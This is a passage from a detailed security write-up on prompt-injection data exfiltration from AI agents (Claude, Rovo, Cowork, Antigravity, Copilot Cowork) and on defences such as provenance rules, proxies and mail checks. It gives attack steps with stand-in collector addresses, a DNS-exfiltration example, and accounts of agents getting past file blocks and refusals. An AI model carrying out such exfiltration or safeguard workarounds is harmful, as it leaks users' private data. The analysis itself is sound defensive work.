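Claude's web fetch tool opens an address only if it has already appeared in the conversation somewhere other than Claude's own writing. Anthropic introduced this provenance rule with the tool in September 2025. The rule requires only a record of the conversation, without the crawler that OpenAI needs for its index of public addresses. Anthropic tightened the rule in July 2026, after Ayush Paul built a website that extracted a user's name from the links Claude followed.

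### Why an added secret fails

The tool reads web pages and PDF files. Claude names an address, Anthropic's servers fetch the page, and its text joins the context. Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, the guide for developers who build on Claude, lists where an address may come from:

- a user message
- the result of a tool that the developer's own software runs
- the result of an earlier web search or web fetch

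Suppose Claude knows the code name "marmalade" and reads a page containing an injected instruction to add the code name to `collector.example/log?w=` and open the result. The page contains the first part of the address, but the full address, `collector.example/log?w=marmalade`, has not appeared in the conversation, so the tool returns an error and sends no request. The tool also blocks the address with the word spelled backwards, because that address has not appeared either.

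The guide also excludes addresses from programs that Claude runs on Anthropic's servers. Otherwise an injection could get Claude to write a one-line program that prints the full address. The printout would be a tool result, so the address would count as having appeared in the conversation.

A developer's own tools can bring this problem back. For example, if a tool saves a note and returns the saved text, Claude could save the full address as a note, and the address would then appear in a permitted tool result. The guide makes no exception for repeated text, so developers should remove addresses from any result that repeats what Claude wrote.

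### User messages that no user wrote

Willison (2025) liked the idea of a tool that opens only addresses from the user's own prompts, but found that Anthropic's rule was looser. In the API, which developers' software uses to send text to Claude, a "user message" is any text that the software labels as one. An email application might put the user's question and a stranger's whole email into one message, and every address in the email would then count as the user's. The same problem arises when a developer's mail tool returns a stranger's email in its results.

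The attacker still cannot steal a secret by having Claude add it to an address. Willison thinks the ban on composed addresses is the part of the rule that protects most against common attacks. But an attacker can supply complete addresses, one for each letter, as Radware did with ChatGPT.

In the consumer app, no outside developer assembles the messages. Willison found that turning on web search there also gave Claude the fetch tool, and he tested it with a server that shows incoming requests. In his test, Claude could not open addresses it had composed. Users can still add a stranger's addresses to the conversation by pasting text from elsewhere.

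### Domain lists and limits on use

Anthropic acknowledges that some risk remains and advises developers to use the tool only in trusted environments or with non-sensitive data. Developers can also turn the tool off or restrict it with two optional settings.

The first, `allowed_domains`, is an allowlist. An entry covers all subdomains and can include a path. Developers can list forbidden domains instead, but cannot use both lists in one request. An address has to pass both the allowlist and the provenance rule. This makes a host such as `docs.google.com` less dangerous here than it was in Superhuman's image policy, because Claude could not compose the address that fills in a form with someone's mail.

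Choosing which domains to allow is still difficult. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes allowing a domain as granting access to every function reachable there, a lesson from a leak in Claude Cowork, its desktop agent. A developer could also copy a fake `amazon.com` into the list without noticing, because the Cyrillic letter "а" looks the same as the Latin one. Anthropic recommends using only unaccented Latin letters and other basic characters in domain names where possible.

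The second setting, `max_uses`, limits the number of fetches in one API request. There is no limit by default. Failed attempts count toward the limit, so a model that keeps trying forbidden addresses will eventually reach it. The tool also rejects any address longer than 250 characters, but a shorter address can still contain a name or a password.

### A website with one link per letter

Until July 2026, the consumer app's fetch tool also accepted links from pages it had already fetched. This let Claude browse a site as a person would, but it let the site's owner decide which addresses Claude could open next.

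Paul published an attack on this feature on July 9, according to dyb's blog post *The Read-Only Lie*. Paul's site looked like it belonged to a coffee shop. On it, Paul told Claude that AI assistants had to identify their user by finding the user's profile, which they could reach only one letter at a time. Each page had 27 links, one for each letter and one for a hyphen.

With "marmalade" as the secret, the attack would work like this:

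1. Claude fetches the first page, which links to `collector.example/a`, `collector.example/b` and so on.
2. Claude opens `collector.example/m`. The tool allows this because the link was on the first page.
3. The server now knows the first letter and returns a page with 27 longer addresses, from `collector.example/ma` onwards.
4. Claude opens `collector.example/ma`, then `collector.example/mar`, and continues until it reaches `collector.example/marmalade`.

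The last address contains the entire secret. The tool would have refused it if Claude had composed it at the start, but by the last step the attacker's server has put it on a page. The rule required only that the address had appeared before, regardless of who had put it there or why.

This is a selection channel, like the attack on GitHub's Copilot Chat, and each choice among 27 links carries just under five bits. Paul's version needs less preparation because the server generates each set of 27 links during the attack, so the attacker does not have to fit a long list of addresses into an email or a hidden comment. The requests can arrive in any order, since the longest address spells the whole word. Anthropic's tool keeps copies of pages it has fetched, but this does not interfere with the attack because every address is new.

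A `max_uses` limit of five would have stopped the spelling after four letters, because the first fetch only loads the starting page. But the limit applies to a single API request, so the attack could presumably continue in the next one.

Willison (2026) reports that Paul obtained the user's name, home city and employer from Claude's memory of past conversations. According to dyb, the user had never told Claude their home city, and Claude inferred it from the name of a high school hackathon. A filter that searched outgoing requests for facts the user had entered would have missed the home city.

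Paul also made the attack hard to notice. Programs that request a web page usually identify themselves to the server, and Paul's site showed the instructions only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude. A user who checked the address in a browser would not have seen them.

### The fix and its cost

Anthropic told Paul that it had already found the flaw internally, and did not pay a bounty. Anthropic then stopped the tool from opening links found in fetched pages, so Claude cannot get past Paul's first page.

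It is less clear whether the fix also covers the API. In August 2026, Anthropic's Japanese developer guide still listed earlier fetch results as a permitted source of addresses. The translation may have been out of date, but developers whose applications handle private data should test this themselves.

The fix makes Claude worse at reading anything spread over several web pages. If a user gives Claude the contents page of a software manual, Claude can no longer follow its links to the chapters. It also can't open the second page of an article or check a source the article links to. The user can paste each new address into the chat, but this becomes tedious after a few pages.

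Claude can also look for the page with web search, because the fetch tool still accepts addresses from search results. Anthropic describes this as the normal method when a user names a document without giving its address. It should work well for a popular manual, but not for a page that the search engine has not indexed.

As a compromise, dyb proposed letting Claude follow links only on domains that the user names in the conversation. Claude could then read manuals again, with one extra step. This would not protect a user who gives Claude the coffee shop's address and asks about its opening hours, because the user would have named the attacker's domain.

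Another of dyb's suggestions is to watch for a series of addresses on one host, each one character longer than the last. Ordinary numbered pages can look similar, so the detector would raise false alarms. An attacker could also avoid detection by replacing the letters with random codes of equal length, since only the attacker's server has to be able to decode them.

### Atlassian Rovo: search off, fetching on

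Rovo is the AI assistant in Atlassian's workplace software, which includes Jira for tracking tasks and Confluence for internal documents. In August 2026, PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls* showed that Rovo had no equivalent of Anthropic's rule and would open any address, including one it had just written.

In PromptArmor's test, a user uploads a guide found online and asks Rovo to organize some Jira tickets. The guide contains hidden instructions. Rovo searches Jira and Confluence, adds what it finds to an address on the attacker's server, and opens that address. The server's log then contains the tickets and documents. If the user returns to the chat later, they see only the suggested ticket changes. Claude's tool would have blocked the request because the full address had never appeared in the conversation.

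Atlassian lets administrators turn off web search for the whole organization, but the attack worked with search turned off. The setting controlled only searches of public websites, and the attack sent the data out through a separate tool for opening addresses, which stayed available. An administrator could reasonably have assumed that turning off web search also stopped Rovo from contacting websites.

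PromptArmor calls the attack zero-click, but The Hacker News (2026) disagrees because the victim has to give Rovo the hostile content and make a request. Neither action is unusual, and PromptArmor says the instructions could also arrive in a support ticket, without an upload. Both sources agree that Rovo sent the data without asking for approval.

PromptArmor reported the problem on May 23, 2026. Atlassian opened a case and thanked PromptArmor but sent nothing further in more than two months, and Rovo was still vulnerable when PromptArmor published. Rovo also displayed Markdown images from its answers, which could give attackers another way to send data out, although PromptArmor did not demonstrate a complete attack that way.

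Atlassian did repair a different Rovo flaw that summer. Mascellino (2026), in *Researchers Uncover RovoBlast Vulnerability in Atlassian AI Assistant*, describes a crafted link that put an attacker's instructions into Rovo's chat when the victim clicked it. Internal data then left through ResearchAgent, a part of Rovo that browses websites by itself. According to Varonis' *RovoBlast*, this browsing ability turned access to that data into a leak.

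Bugcrowd's *One-Click Data Exfiltration via rovoChatPrompt URL Parameter (Confluence / Rovo)* (2026) lists the flaw as reported on November 4, 2025, and fixed on July 8, 2026. The fix stopped crafted links from inserting and running an attacker's instructions in Rovo, but PromptArmor's attack, which came in through an uploaded file, still worked a month later. A check on addresses the assistant composes would have worked against PromptArmor's attack however the instructions arrived.

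Customers cannot remove Rovo completely. Varonis advises them to turn off browsing agents they don't need and to block Rovo's access to legal, financial and personnel files.

### Already in the conversation or already public

Anthropic's rule and OpenAI's index both stop the attack that worked on Rovo, but they differ on other addresses:

| Address | Claude, after the July fix | ChatGPT |
|---|---|---|
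| Composed by the model, with private data added | Refused | Warning, or the model tries another site |
| New or unlisted page, with the address typed by the user | Opened | Opened |
| Public page linked from a page just read | Refused, unless it also appears in a search result or another permitted source | Opened |
| Attacker's new address, in an email that a tool returned | Opened, if the developer's own software runs the tool | Warning, or the model tries another site |

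The index protects better against planted addresses than the conversation rule does, because an attacker's email or a poorly designed tool can put an address into the conversation without making it public.

The index would also have blocked Paul's original design. Spelling out any ten-character name one letter at a time would require the crawler to find a page for every possible combination, about 206 trillion for the last step alone. An attacker could instead publish numbered pages like Radware's, but under Anthropic's rule their addresses would also have to appear in Claude's search results or arrive through a message or tool.

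Anthropic's July fix brought Claude's rule closer to ChatGPT's. In the consumer app, Claude can now open only addresses that the user supplied or that a search returned, and addresses from search results are usually public. ChatGPT can open any address in OpenAI's index without searching for it first, which makes it better at following links.

Anthropic's rule is much easier to build than OpenAI's index, for which a company such as Atlassian would need a crawler or access to someone else's. With Anthropic's rule, the company would only have to store the addresses from permitted sources and compare each new request with them.

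## Claude Cowork and Google Antigravity: domain allowlists for agents that run code

Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office work, and Antigravity, Google's code editor, can both run programs. Each had a list of approved domains that was supposed to keep private data from leaving, but researchers got data out through a domain on each list. In Cowork the domain was Anthropic's own API, and in Antigravity it was webhook.site, a service that records every request it receives.

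### Why a check on one tool is not enough

If an assistant can reach the web only through a fetch tool, a developer can check every address in that tool. An agent that runs commands has many other ways to send data out. It can make web requests with `curl`, upload code with `git`, or write a short program that does either. A rule on the fetch tool doesn't cover any of these.

*Takedown* (Lee, Kim and colleagues, 2025) examined eight widely used, unnamed coding agents. Four had a built-in tool for fetching web pages, and one of these opened pages without the user's approval. Another always asked first, but it also accepted tools from extensions and let each extension's developer decide whether its tools would ask. Of the ten most-installed extensions with such tools, seven did not ask, including a web search extension from Microsoft. In four of the eight agents, the researchers could steal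 files from anywhere on the computer without any approval from the user.

One of the eight agents used an operating system feature to block network calls from its commands. That stops leaks but also prevents the agent from downloading packages, so Lee and colleagues suggest a list of permitted addresses.

Checks on the model's input can also fail. In February 2026, a member of Anthropic's internal attack team emailed an employee a prompt to paste into Claude Code, the company's coding agent. The prompt included ordinary setup steps, but it also told Claude to read the employee's cloud credentials and send them to an outside server. Anthropic reports that Claude did so in 24 of 25 runs. Because the instructions came from the user, a detector looking for a stranger's commands would not have caught them. Anthropic concluded that only limits on the agent's file access and network traffic would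 have stopped the attack.

### A sandbox with one exit

The usual design gives the agent's commands no network connection except to a proxy, which holds the list of permitted domains. Anthropic's documentation for Claude Code, as of October 2026, describes how this works:

1. The operating system starts each command inside a sandbox. On Linux the sandbox has its own network with no link to the real one, and on macOS the system blocks connections to anything but the proxy.
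2. Standard settings tell programs in the sandbox to send their web traffic to the proxy, which runs outside it.
3. The proxy compares the requested host with the list, then connects or refuses.

A program that ignores the settings fails because it has no other route to the network, and this includes harmless programs such as most database clients. The limits also apply to every program that a command starts, so a malicious helper hidden in a software package could not upload files to an unlisted host.

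The list of allowed domains starts empty, and Claude Code asks the user the first time a command needs a new domain. The sandbox is off by default and covers only shell commands, so the list does not restrict Claude's fetch tool or the local programs that supply extra tools. When a command fails inside the sandbox, Claude may offer to run it again outside, and if the user agrees, that command runs without the sandbox's protection. Administrators can require the sandbox and turn off these retries.

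### What encryption hides from the proxy

To open an encrypted connection, a program first sends a request that the proxy can read, such as `CONNECT pictures.example:443`, where 443 is the port normally used for encrypted web traffic. If the list permits the host, the proxy opens the connection and passes encrypted data in both directions. The encryption hides the path and the content from the proxy, as well as whether the program is downloading or uploading and whose account it uses.

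The proxy relies on the host name that the program puts in its request. Large content delivery networks serve many websites from the same machines. A program can ask the proxy for a permitted site on such a network and then, inside the encrypted connection, request a different site that the attacker runs there. This is called domain fronting, and it works only if the network's operator allows the mismatch. Docker, which also provides sandboxes for agents, describes the weakness as inherent to proxying encrypted traffic.

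Docker and Anthropic warn about allowing broad domains such as `github.com`. Developers need GitHub constantly, but anyone can open an account there and receive data. A proxy with access only to the hostname cannot distinguish the attacker's project from the user's.

### What decrypting costs

A decrypting proxy ends the program's encrypted connection at the proxy and opens a second one to the real server, so it has to impersonate that server. *Codex CLI Network Proxy* (Vaughan, 2026) describes how OpenAI's coding agent can do this by generating a certificate for each host when a program asks to connect to it.

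Anthropic notes that some common tools, including GitHub's command-line program, may fail certificate checks inside the macOS sandbox. Users who inspect traffic with their own decrypting proxy can fix this by turning on `enableWeakerNetworkIsolation`, but doing so loosens the sandbox.

Decryption also doesn't help until someone writes rules for the decrypted traffic. Claude Code has an experimental setting that decrypts connections but does not filter their content. Organizations that want a content filter have to supply their own proxy, and Claude Code's domain rules then do not apply to traffic sent to that proxy.

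### DNS lookups

A DNS lookup, which finds a host's numeric address, can carry data by itself. Suppose a program in a sandbox looks up this name:

`marmalade.collector.example`

The nearest DNS server has no record of the name, so the lookup goes to the server responsible for `collector.example`. The attacker runs that server and reads the word in its log. The program never has to connect to the attacker's host, so a rule that restricts connections doesn't stop this. A name can have up to 253 characters, enough for a password, and a program can split a longer file across many lookups.

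The hidden channel in ChatGPT's Python sandbox used domain name lookups, which OpenAI had left available while blocking normal web traffic, according to The Jerusalem Post. Check Point Research found that the channel could also carry an attacker's commands into the sandbox.

Amazon's AgentCore Code Interpreter, a cloud service that runs code for AI agents, had the same gap. BeyondTrust's *AWS Bedrock AgentCore Code Interpreter’s ‘Sandbox’ mode allows DNS queries* (2026) says that Amazon had advertised Sandbox mode as "complete isolation", much as Microsoft had promised for the Copilot sandbox that ReLeak broke. A leak could be severe because the default permissions in the standard starter kit could give the interpreter full access to stored passwords and read access to every file store in the customer's account, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Security Flaw in AWS Bedrock Code Interpreter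 Raises Alarms*. BeyondTrust published its findings on March 16, 2026, and added on April 22 that Amazon had since closed the gap.

It is safer for the proxy to do DNS lookups. Commands in Claude Code's sandbox cannot send UDP traffic, which DNS normally uses. The proxy looks up a name only after the name has passed the domain list, so a name containing a secret gets no further than the proxy. It then refuses the request if the name leads only to local addresses, such as the one where cloud machines get their credentials.

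### Claude Cowork: uploading to the vendor's own API

Rehberger found the weakness before Cowork existed. In autumn 2025, Anthropic let Claude's chat app make network requests from the sandbox where it runs code. The default setting, "Package managers only", allowed requests to a short list of domains that programs download software from. The first domain on the list was `api.anthropic.com`.

Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate* explains how an attacker could use that entry. Instructions hidden in a document told Claude to copy the user's latest conversation into a file and upload it through Anthropic's Files API. The instructions included the attacker's API key, so the file went to the attacker's Anthropic account. One upload could carry 30 megabytes, thousands of times more than a web address can hold. Claude often refused when it noticed the key, until Rehberger surrounded the upload code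 with harmless lines, such as one that prints "Hello, world".

Rehberger reported this on October 25, 2025. The report was closed within an hour as out of scope because it concerned "model safety". On October 30, Anthropic said such leaks were in scope and blamed an error in its process, but it did not fix the problem before releasing Cowork in January 2026.

Cowork works on folders that the user selects and ran its code in a virtual machine, a simulated computer separate from the real one. Two days after the release, PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* showed the same leak there:

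- The user connects a folder of real estate documents and uploads a Word file that appears to contain instructions for analyzing them. The injection is in tiny white text.
- When the user asks for the analysis, Claude runs a `curl` command that uploads the largest file to the attacker's Anthropic account.
- The proxy permits the connection because it goes to `api.anthropic.com`, and nobody has to approve it.

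The stolen loan estimate included financial figures and parts of Social Security numbers. PromptArmor ran this attack on Claude Haiku, a small model, but a different attack worked on Opus 4.5, which was known to resist injections better. Anthropic acknowledged the risk and said it would update the virtual machine, according to *Anthropic Claude Vulnerability Exposes Cowork AI to Data Exfiltration via Prompt Injection* (Apostol, 2026).

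### Binding the domain to the user's session

Anthropic could not remove its API from the allowlist because Cowork needs it to reach the model. Instead, it added a second proxy that decrypts traffic to the API and accepts only requests with the session token issued to that virtual machine, so an upload with an attacker's key now fails. Rehberger had proposed the same restriction in October. The proxy also rejects headers that could turn the API into a relay by making Anthropic's servers fetch an outside address.

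Anthropic put this check inside the virtual machine because its servers could not distinguish a Cowork request from any other customer's. But a program that took control of the whole machine could presumably tamper with the check.

By October 2026, most Cowork sessions no longer ran on the user's computer. Anthropic's *Claude Cowork architecture overview* describes temporary sandboxes on Anthropic's servers. Programs in a sandbox cannot change or bypass the proxy outside it. The only credentials in the sandbox are tokens that expire within hours, and the user's credentials for connected services never enter it. For Enterprise customers, sandboxes have no network access by default. The overview does not say whether the new proxy also rejects other people's API keys.

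A network setting may also not cover every request an agent makes. In March 2026, an Anthropic help page warned that Cowork's network limits did not apply to web search. Since May 29, administrators have been able to control which hosts Cowork may fetch from when it processes search results, according to PromptArmor's change log. Other settings can also add entries to the allowlist. If a company runs Claude Desktop with models hosted by another provider and leaves optional usage statistics on, the app adds `api.anthropic.com` to the agent's allowlist, according to Anthropic's documentation.

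### Antigravity: a request logger on the default list

Webhook.site gives anyone a web address and displays every request sent to it. Developers use it to test whether their software sends the right data. It is an even simpler relay than Google Forms because it is designed to display incoming data. When Google released Antigravity in November 2025, the default allowlist for the agent's browser included Webhook.site.

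In PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data*, a developer gives the agent an online guide to accounting software. The guide contains instructions in one-point type for the agent to collect code and credentials, add them to a webhook.site address, and open the resulting URL in the browser.

The credentials were in a file named `.env`. The developer had marked it as private, so Antigravity's file-reading tool blocked the model, Gemini, from opening it. Gemini then printed the file with the terminal command `cat`, which the restriction did not cover.

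The browser's allowlist has the same limitation. Willison wondered whether `curl` would have worked instead of the browser, and PromptArmor found three other leaks that did not need the browser. Antigravity later gained a sandbox for terminal commands, but it was off by default and available only on macOS, according to Google's documentation as quoted on DeepakNess, a developer's blog. The post is undated and may not reflect the current version.

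With the recommended settings, the agent chose when to ask for human review. Google displayed a warning about the risk of data theft and listed such leaks among Antigravity's "known issues", for which it pays no bug bounty. Google said it was working on fixes. PromptArmor therefore published without first reporting the flaw privately.

Later evidence does not clearly show that the problem was fixed. Agentpedia, a guide to AI agents, stated in March 2026 that webhook.site was still on the default list. Google's documentation page *Allowlist / Denylist*, in a copy from May, describes a list that users edit themselves and can choose to fill with default entries. A separate service blocks hosts that Google considers dangerous, and the browser cannot open anything if that service is unavailable. But webhook.site is a legitimate tool, so the service may well not block it. In *Faking the Pipeline*,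 Odson and Morris (2026) also got data out in June through images in the chat, a route that Google had called intended behavior the previous November.

### Narrower rules than a domain

An allowlist can be stricter about what a program does at a permitted host, or about who permits the host and for how long. The two leaks show how much depends on the kind of rule:

| Rule | Cowork upload | Antigravity request |
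|---|---|---|
| Accept only the user's own credentials | Blocked | No effect, since the request needs no account |
| Permit only read requests | Blocked, if the proxy decrypts | Allowed |
| Ask before each new domain | No question, since the domain is on the list | No question, for the same reason |

Anthropic could easily build a rule that allows only requests made with the user's own credentials, because it issues the tokens and runs the API. To apply the same rule to GitHub, an operator would have to know how every kind of request identifies its account. The rule also fails if the user's own account can post in public projects.

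Claude Code has a related feature that replaces a password with a placeholder inside the sandbox. The proxy inserts the real password only in requests to hosts the user has chosen, so an injected command can steal only the useless placeholder. The feature does not stop an attacker from supplying a different password, as in the Cowork attack. It can also break some requests to Amazon's cloud, which must carry a signature computed with the real credentials.

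**Read-only requests.** OpenAI's Codex has a "limited" mode that permits only three request methods, including GET. Vaughan recommends it for research and reading documentation. The mode blocks encrypted uploads only if the proxy decrypts them, and a GET request can still carry data in its address, as the request to webhook.site did.

Requiring the user to approve each domain can stop a leak to an unfamiliar host if the user reads the request. According to Anthropic, Claude Code's users approved about 93% of permission requests of all kinds, and its sandbox reduced the number of requests by 84%. With fewer requests, users can look more carefully at an unfamiliar domain. But the request shows only a host, and a sensible user would have approved `api.anthropic.com`.

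Some users also dislike being asked to approve each site. In the forum thread *Web lookups now require authorization per site?*, a user of the code editor Cursor called a per-site allowlist "pretty useless" and asked for a way to permit the whole web. In *Browser Allow List not available*, an Antigravity user described adding hundreds of addresses by hand. After that many approvals, hardly anyone will remember what each host can do.

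One remedy is to make approvals expire. In Claude Code's auto mode, Claude names the hosts a command needs, a second model reviews the command and its hosts, and the permission ends when the command does. This prevents a long list from building up, though an attacker may be able to deceive the second model too. Cursor 2.5 instead lets developers keep a separate list for each project. In the forum thread *Cursor 2.5*, one developer wrote that most projects needed only a package registry and a couple of API addresses. With a list that short, it is practical to check whether each entry is a service that accepts data from anyone.

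## Outbound email: Microsoft Copilot Cowork and the checks a mail tool needs

Checking an email's recipients can miss data theft, although it looks easier than checking a web address because the email lists them. Microsoft Copilot Cowork, an agent that sends mail, posts in Teams and manages files, asks the user to approve messages before it sends them, except when the user is the only recipient. In May 2026 PromptArmor published an attack that stole files through messages sent only to the user, which needed no approval.

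### A message to the user's own account

Copilot Cowork runs on Anthropic's Claude models and has a similar name to Claude Cowork, but it works in Microsoft's cloud with the user's permissions. PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* found that it sends emails and Teams messages to the active user immediately, and that users have no setting to change this. This exception for messages to oneself seems reasonable, because people like to get a daily briefing in their inbox and such a message reveals nothing to anyone else.

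The attack began with a skill, a file of instructions for a task the user repeats:

1. The user uploads a skill found online. Five of its 81 lines are an injection.
2. The user asks for a review of the week's work, and Cowork loads the skill.
3. Cowork retrieves a "pre-authenticated" download link for each file it finds. Anyone who has such a link can download the file without logging in.
4. Cowork sends the user a Teams message containing images. Their addresses point to the attacker's server, with the download links in the query strings.
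5. The user opens the message, the app requests the images, and the attacker downloads the files.

A recipient check wouldn't stop the message in step 4, because the data goes to the image host, which isn't on the recipient list, and leaves only when the user opens the message. The download links also get around the usual limit on how much data a web address can carry, since a link of ordinary length gives access to a whole file.

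The attack worked in all five of PromptArmor's trials, in which Cowork chose automatically between Claude Opus 4.7 and the smaller Sonnet 4.6. When PromptArmor selected Opus 4.7, the same injection stole more data, because the model searched more thoroughly and included every document from that week's earlier Cowork sessions. The activity log listed the Teams action but did not show the message text. A weekly review is the sort of task people schedule, and a scheduled task would repeat the theft without anyone watching the agent.

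The direct fix is to remove remote images from any message the agent writes. Copying each image into the message would not help if Microsoft's servers had to fetch it first, because that fetch would send the data to the attacker. PromptArmor instead suggests that administrators block downloads from sensitive SharePoint sites, so that Cowork cannot get the links. But this policy greatly restricts users, who can then view the files only in a browser and cannot print them or open them in Word or Excel.

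### Microsoft's response

PromptArmor presented its findings as a risk of the product's design, not a specific bug, and its article lists no fix. Microsoft's public description of the approval step stayed much the same. Microsoft's *Copilot Cowork overview* (2026), dated September 8, said "You approve each action before it happens", without mentioning an exception for messages to oneself. By then Cowork was no longer in preview for work and school accounts.

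According to PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Controlled by Attacker, Bypassing Sandbox*, Microsoft confirmed on August 19 that it had dealt with a separate flaw in Cowork's sandbox, reported on June 24. That repair concerned programs reaching the internet and would not affect a picture in a Teams message.

### What a mail check has to read

Each part of an email can carry data out or change who receives it:

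| Part | What can go wrong |
|---|---|
| To and Cc | An outsider appears among colleagues, or a group address has outside members |
| Bcc | A recipient gets a copy without the others knowing |
| Reply address | A colleague gets the message, but the colleague's answer goes to the attacker |
| Subject | It holds private text that a check on the body alone would miss |
| Body | It holds private text, perhaps in white or tiny type |
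| Attachments | A file contains hidden sheets, old comments or its own outside links |
| Remote images | Opening the message sends a request to another host |
| Links | The address contains private data, or a key that opens a file |
| Sharing permissions | The message is harmless, but it gives someone access to a file |

A check on outgoing email has to read the delivery list, the separate list of addresses that mail servers use to deliver a message. The To and Cc lines only show the reader who else received it, and Bcc addresses are normally on the delivery list but nowhere in the message. Many emails also contain their text twice, once plain and once in HTML. A check that reads only the plain version will miss an image in the HTML, which is the version most mail apps display.

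EchoLeak got through Microsoft 365 Copilot partly because two programs interpreted the same Markdown differently. A mail tool can avoid this problem by accepting only a recipient, a subject, plain text and attachment names from the model, and using ordinary code to build the email. The email then has no remote images because the model has no field in which to specify them. This would be too strict for sending HTML newsletters, one of Cowork's advertised uses. For those, the code could offer a fixed layout and accept only pictures from the company's own files, embedded in the message.

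### Messages that do not look like email

A check on the mail tool will not cover every way an office agent can send text to someone. A meeting invitation sends a title and description to everyone invited. Cowork can also decline a meeting and tell the organizer why. A stranger could therefore send the user an invitation with an injection in the description and receive private data in the refusal, even though the user never named the stranger as a recipient.

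Shared documents can have the same effect. Sharing a file gives the recipient its contents, and most office software also sends a notice with the file's name. PromptArmor's *Securing Microsoft Copilot Cowork* (2026) warns that an agent reorganizing folders can move a sensitive file somewhere with looser permissions. People who already have access to the new folder can then read the file, even though no message goes out. The guide also lists interactive cards, whose buttons can submit data to an attacker's server when the user clicks them.

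An Outlook rule that forwards mail can do more lasting damage because it keeps working after the conversation ends. Microsoft's guide to using Cowork says the agent shows a detailed card explaining what a rule will do before the user approves it. Scheduling a meeting and sharing a document also require approval, according to Microsoft's *Explore how Cowork works*.

Developers could write code that works out who will be able to read what after each of these actions. A single policy could then cover emails, invitations and moved files. Otherwise, an attacker whose injection fails with the mail tool can try using the calendar tool instead.

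### Choosing who may receive mail

The simplest recipient rule allows mail only within the organization. A looser rule allows anyone in the user's contacts, and a stricter one allows only people the user named in the request. The stricter rule is a provenance rule. The three rules differ in these situations:

| Recipient | Same organization | Known contacts | Named by the user |
|---|---|---|---|
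| Attacker's unfamiliar address | Block | Block | Block |
| Attacker who has exchanged mail with the user | Block | Allow, if the app saves contacts automatically | Block |
| Colleague the user did not mention | Allow | Allow, if in contacts | Block |
| Customer the user asked to answer | Block | Allow, if in contacts | Allow |
| The user's own account | Allow | Allow | Allow, if the user asked for a message |

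The last row shows why no recipient rule is enough on its own against the Cowork attack. A strict rule could have stopped the attack in PromptArmor's test, because the user asked for a review but not for a message. If the user had asked for the review by email, however, they would have approved the recipient without knowing about the images.

Microsoft's newest control follows the organization rule. KBY Technologies' *MC1583195*, a news article about a notice that Microsoft published on December 7, 2026, describes three settings for email that Cowork sends outside the organization:

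- **Allow**, the default, asks the user to confirm each email. For a recurring task, the user can approve once for all later runs.
- **Require approval** removes that one-time approval, so every run waits for the user.
- **Restrict** saves the email as a draft, and the user has to send it. Administrators can make exceptions for listed domains.

An address counts as external if its domain isn't one of the organization's own, so a sister company on a different domain is external. If one recipient of a message is blocked, Cowork stops the whole message instead of silently removing that recipient. This is sensible because a user who sees "sent" will assume that everyone received it.

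By that definition, an employee's own address is internal, so the new settings would not have stopped PromptArmor's attack. The notice covers only outgoing mail, so it's unclear what happens with invitations or shared files. Restrict may also leave a smaller gap, because if Outlook loads remote images in drafts, a user who opens a suspicious draft to review it will trigger the request.

A rule stated in the prompt is much weaker than any of these because no code enforces it. For example, one of Microsoft's sample prompts for Cowork asks it not to include external attendees on an email. The model will usually comply, but a prompt injection can override the instruction.

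### Following each value to its source

A mail tool that allows only recipients the user named still has to turn "Tom" into an address when the user writes "send this to Tom". If the model does this after reading a stranger's email, it might choose an address from that email. The tool's code should instead look up Tom in the company directory, and it must be able to confirm that the name came from the user.

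CaMeL, a research design Debenedetti and colleagues described in 2025, keeps track of this for a whole task. Suppose the user asks, "Send Tom the agenda from yesterday's meeting notes." One model reads only that request and writes a short program that finds the notes, extracts the agenda, looks up Tom and sends the email. A second model reads the notes and extracts the agenda, but it cannot call any tools. An injection in the notes can change the agenda the second model returns, but it can't add another email to the program.

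A conventional interpreter runs the program and records where each value came from and who may read it. When the program reaches the sending step, the interpreter compares these records with a policy. The recipient came from the user's request and the directory, so it passes. If the address had come from the notes, the policy could block it or require the user's approval. The policy can also check whether Tom may read the notes that the agenda came from.

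The design makes the assistant somewhat less useful. A request such as "Do whatever the client asks in this email" cannot become a complete program until a model has read the email. A request to write to the address at the bottom of a document is ordinary, but the recipient comes from untrusted text, so the policy will often interrupt the user. Someone also has to write a policy for every tool and keep the reading permissions accurate.

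Tracking would have helped in the Cowork case only if the system had treated the skill as untrusted data and the policy had counted an image host as a reader of the message. The injection was in a skill, and Cowork treats skills as instructions. If the planning model had read the skill as part of the user's request, the attacker's steps would have become part of the program. With the image host counted as a reader, the policy would have blocked the message even though its recipient was correct, because the user may read the download links but `collector.example` may not.

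### A mail tool that added its own recipient

CaMeL's interpreter checks the values it passes to a tool but relies on the tool to use them as given. The mail tool postmark-mcp violated this assumption in September 2025. It was an MCP server, a program that connects an assistant to an outside service through the Model Context Protocol standard. According to The Hacker News (2025), it copied a genuine library of the same name that lets assistants send email through the Postmark service.

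Someone using the name "phanpak" published the copy on npm, a public collection of software packages. Koi Security, which discovered the theft, says versions 1.0.0 to 1.0.15 worked properly. Version 1.0.16, released on September 17, added a line of code that put an outside address in the Bcc field of every email. SC Media's *Open-source MCP server package caught stealing emails* put the package's downloads at 1,500 a week. The developer later deleted the package from npm, but Snyk's *Malicious Package Affecting postmark-mcp package, versions >=1.0.16* (2025) advised users to uninstall their copies and replace any passwords they had emailed through it.

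The assistant could call the tool with the correct recipient and text, and the tool then added the extra address. No prompt injection was involved. A check on the tool call would have found nothing wrong, and an approval dialog based on that call would have shown only the intended recipient and text, so the user would have had no reason to reject the email.

The check therefore has to come after the tool, at a point where the final delivery list exists. In ITPro's *A malicious MCP server is silently stealing user emails*, Koi's co-founder Idan Dardikman said that such servers bypass every control, including email gateways. That is true when the mail never passes through the gateway, such as when a tool sends directly through an outside service. But email logs must have recorded the blind copies, or Snyk's advice that users search their logs for messages to the attacker's domain would have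 been useless.

A company can make a mail tool use its gateway by keeping the mail service's password only in the gateway. The tool hands each message to the gateway, which sends it only after checking the delivery list. The network proxy also has to block the tool from contacting other mail services or uploading the text to a website. Both checks are necessary because a malicious tool can still read every message it handles.

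The gateway also needs a record of what the user approved. A rule against all outside recipients would have caught the blind copies, but it would also have blocked mail to customers. A more precise check stores the approved recipients and content before the tool runs and compares them with the outgoing message. An added Bcc address fails this check even if the company writes to that domain every day.

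### What an approval dialog must show

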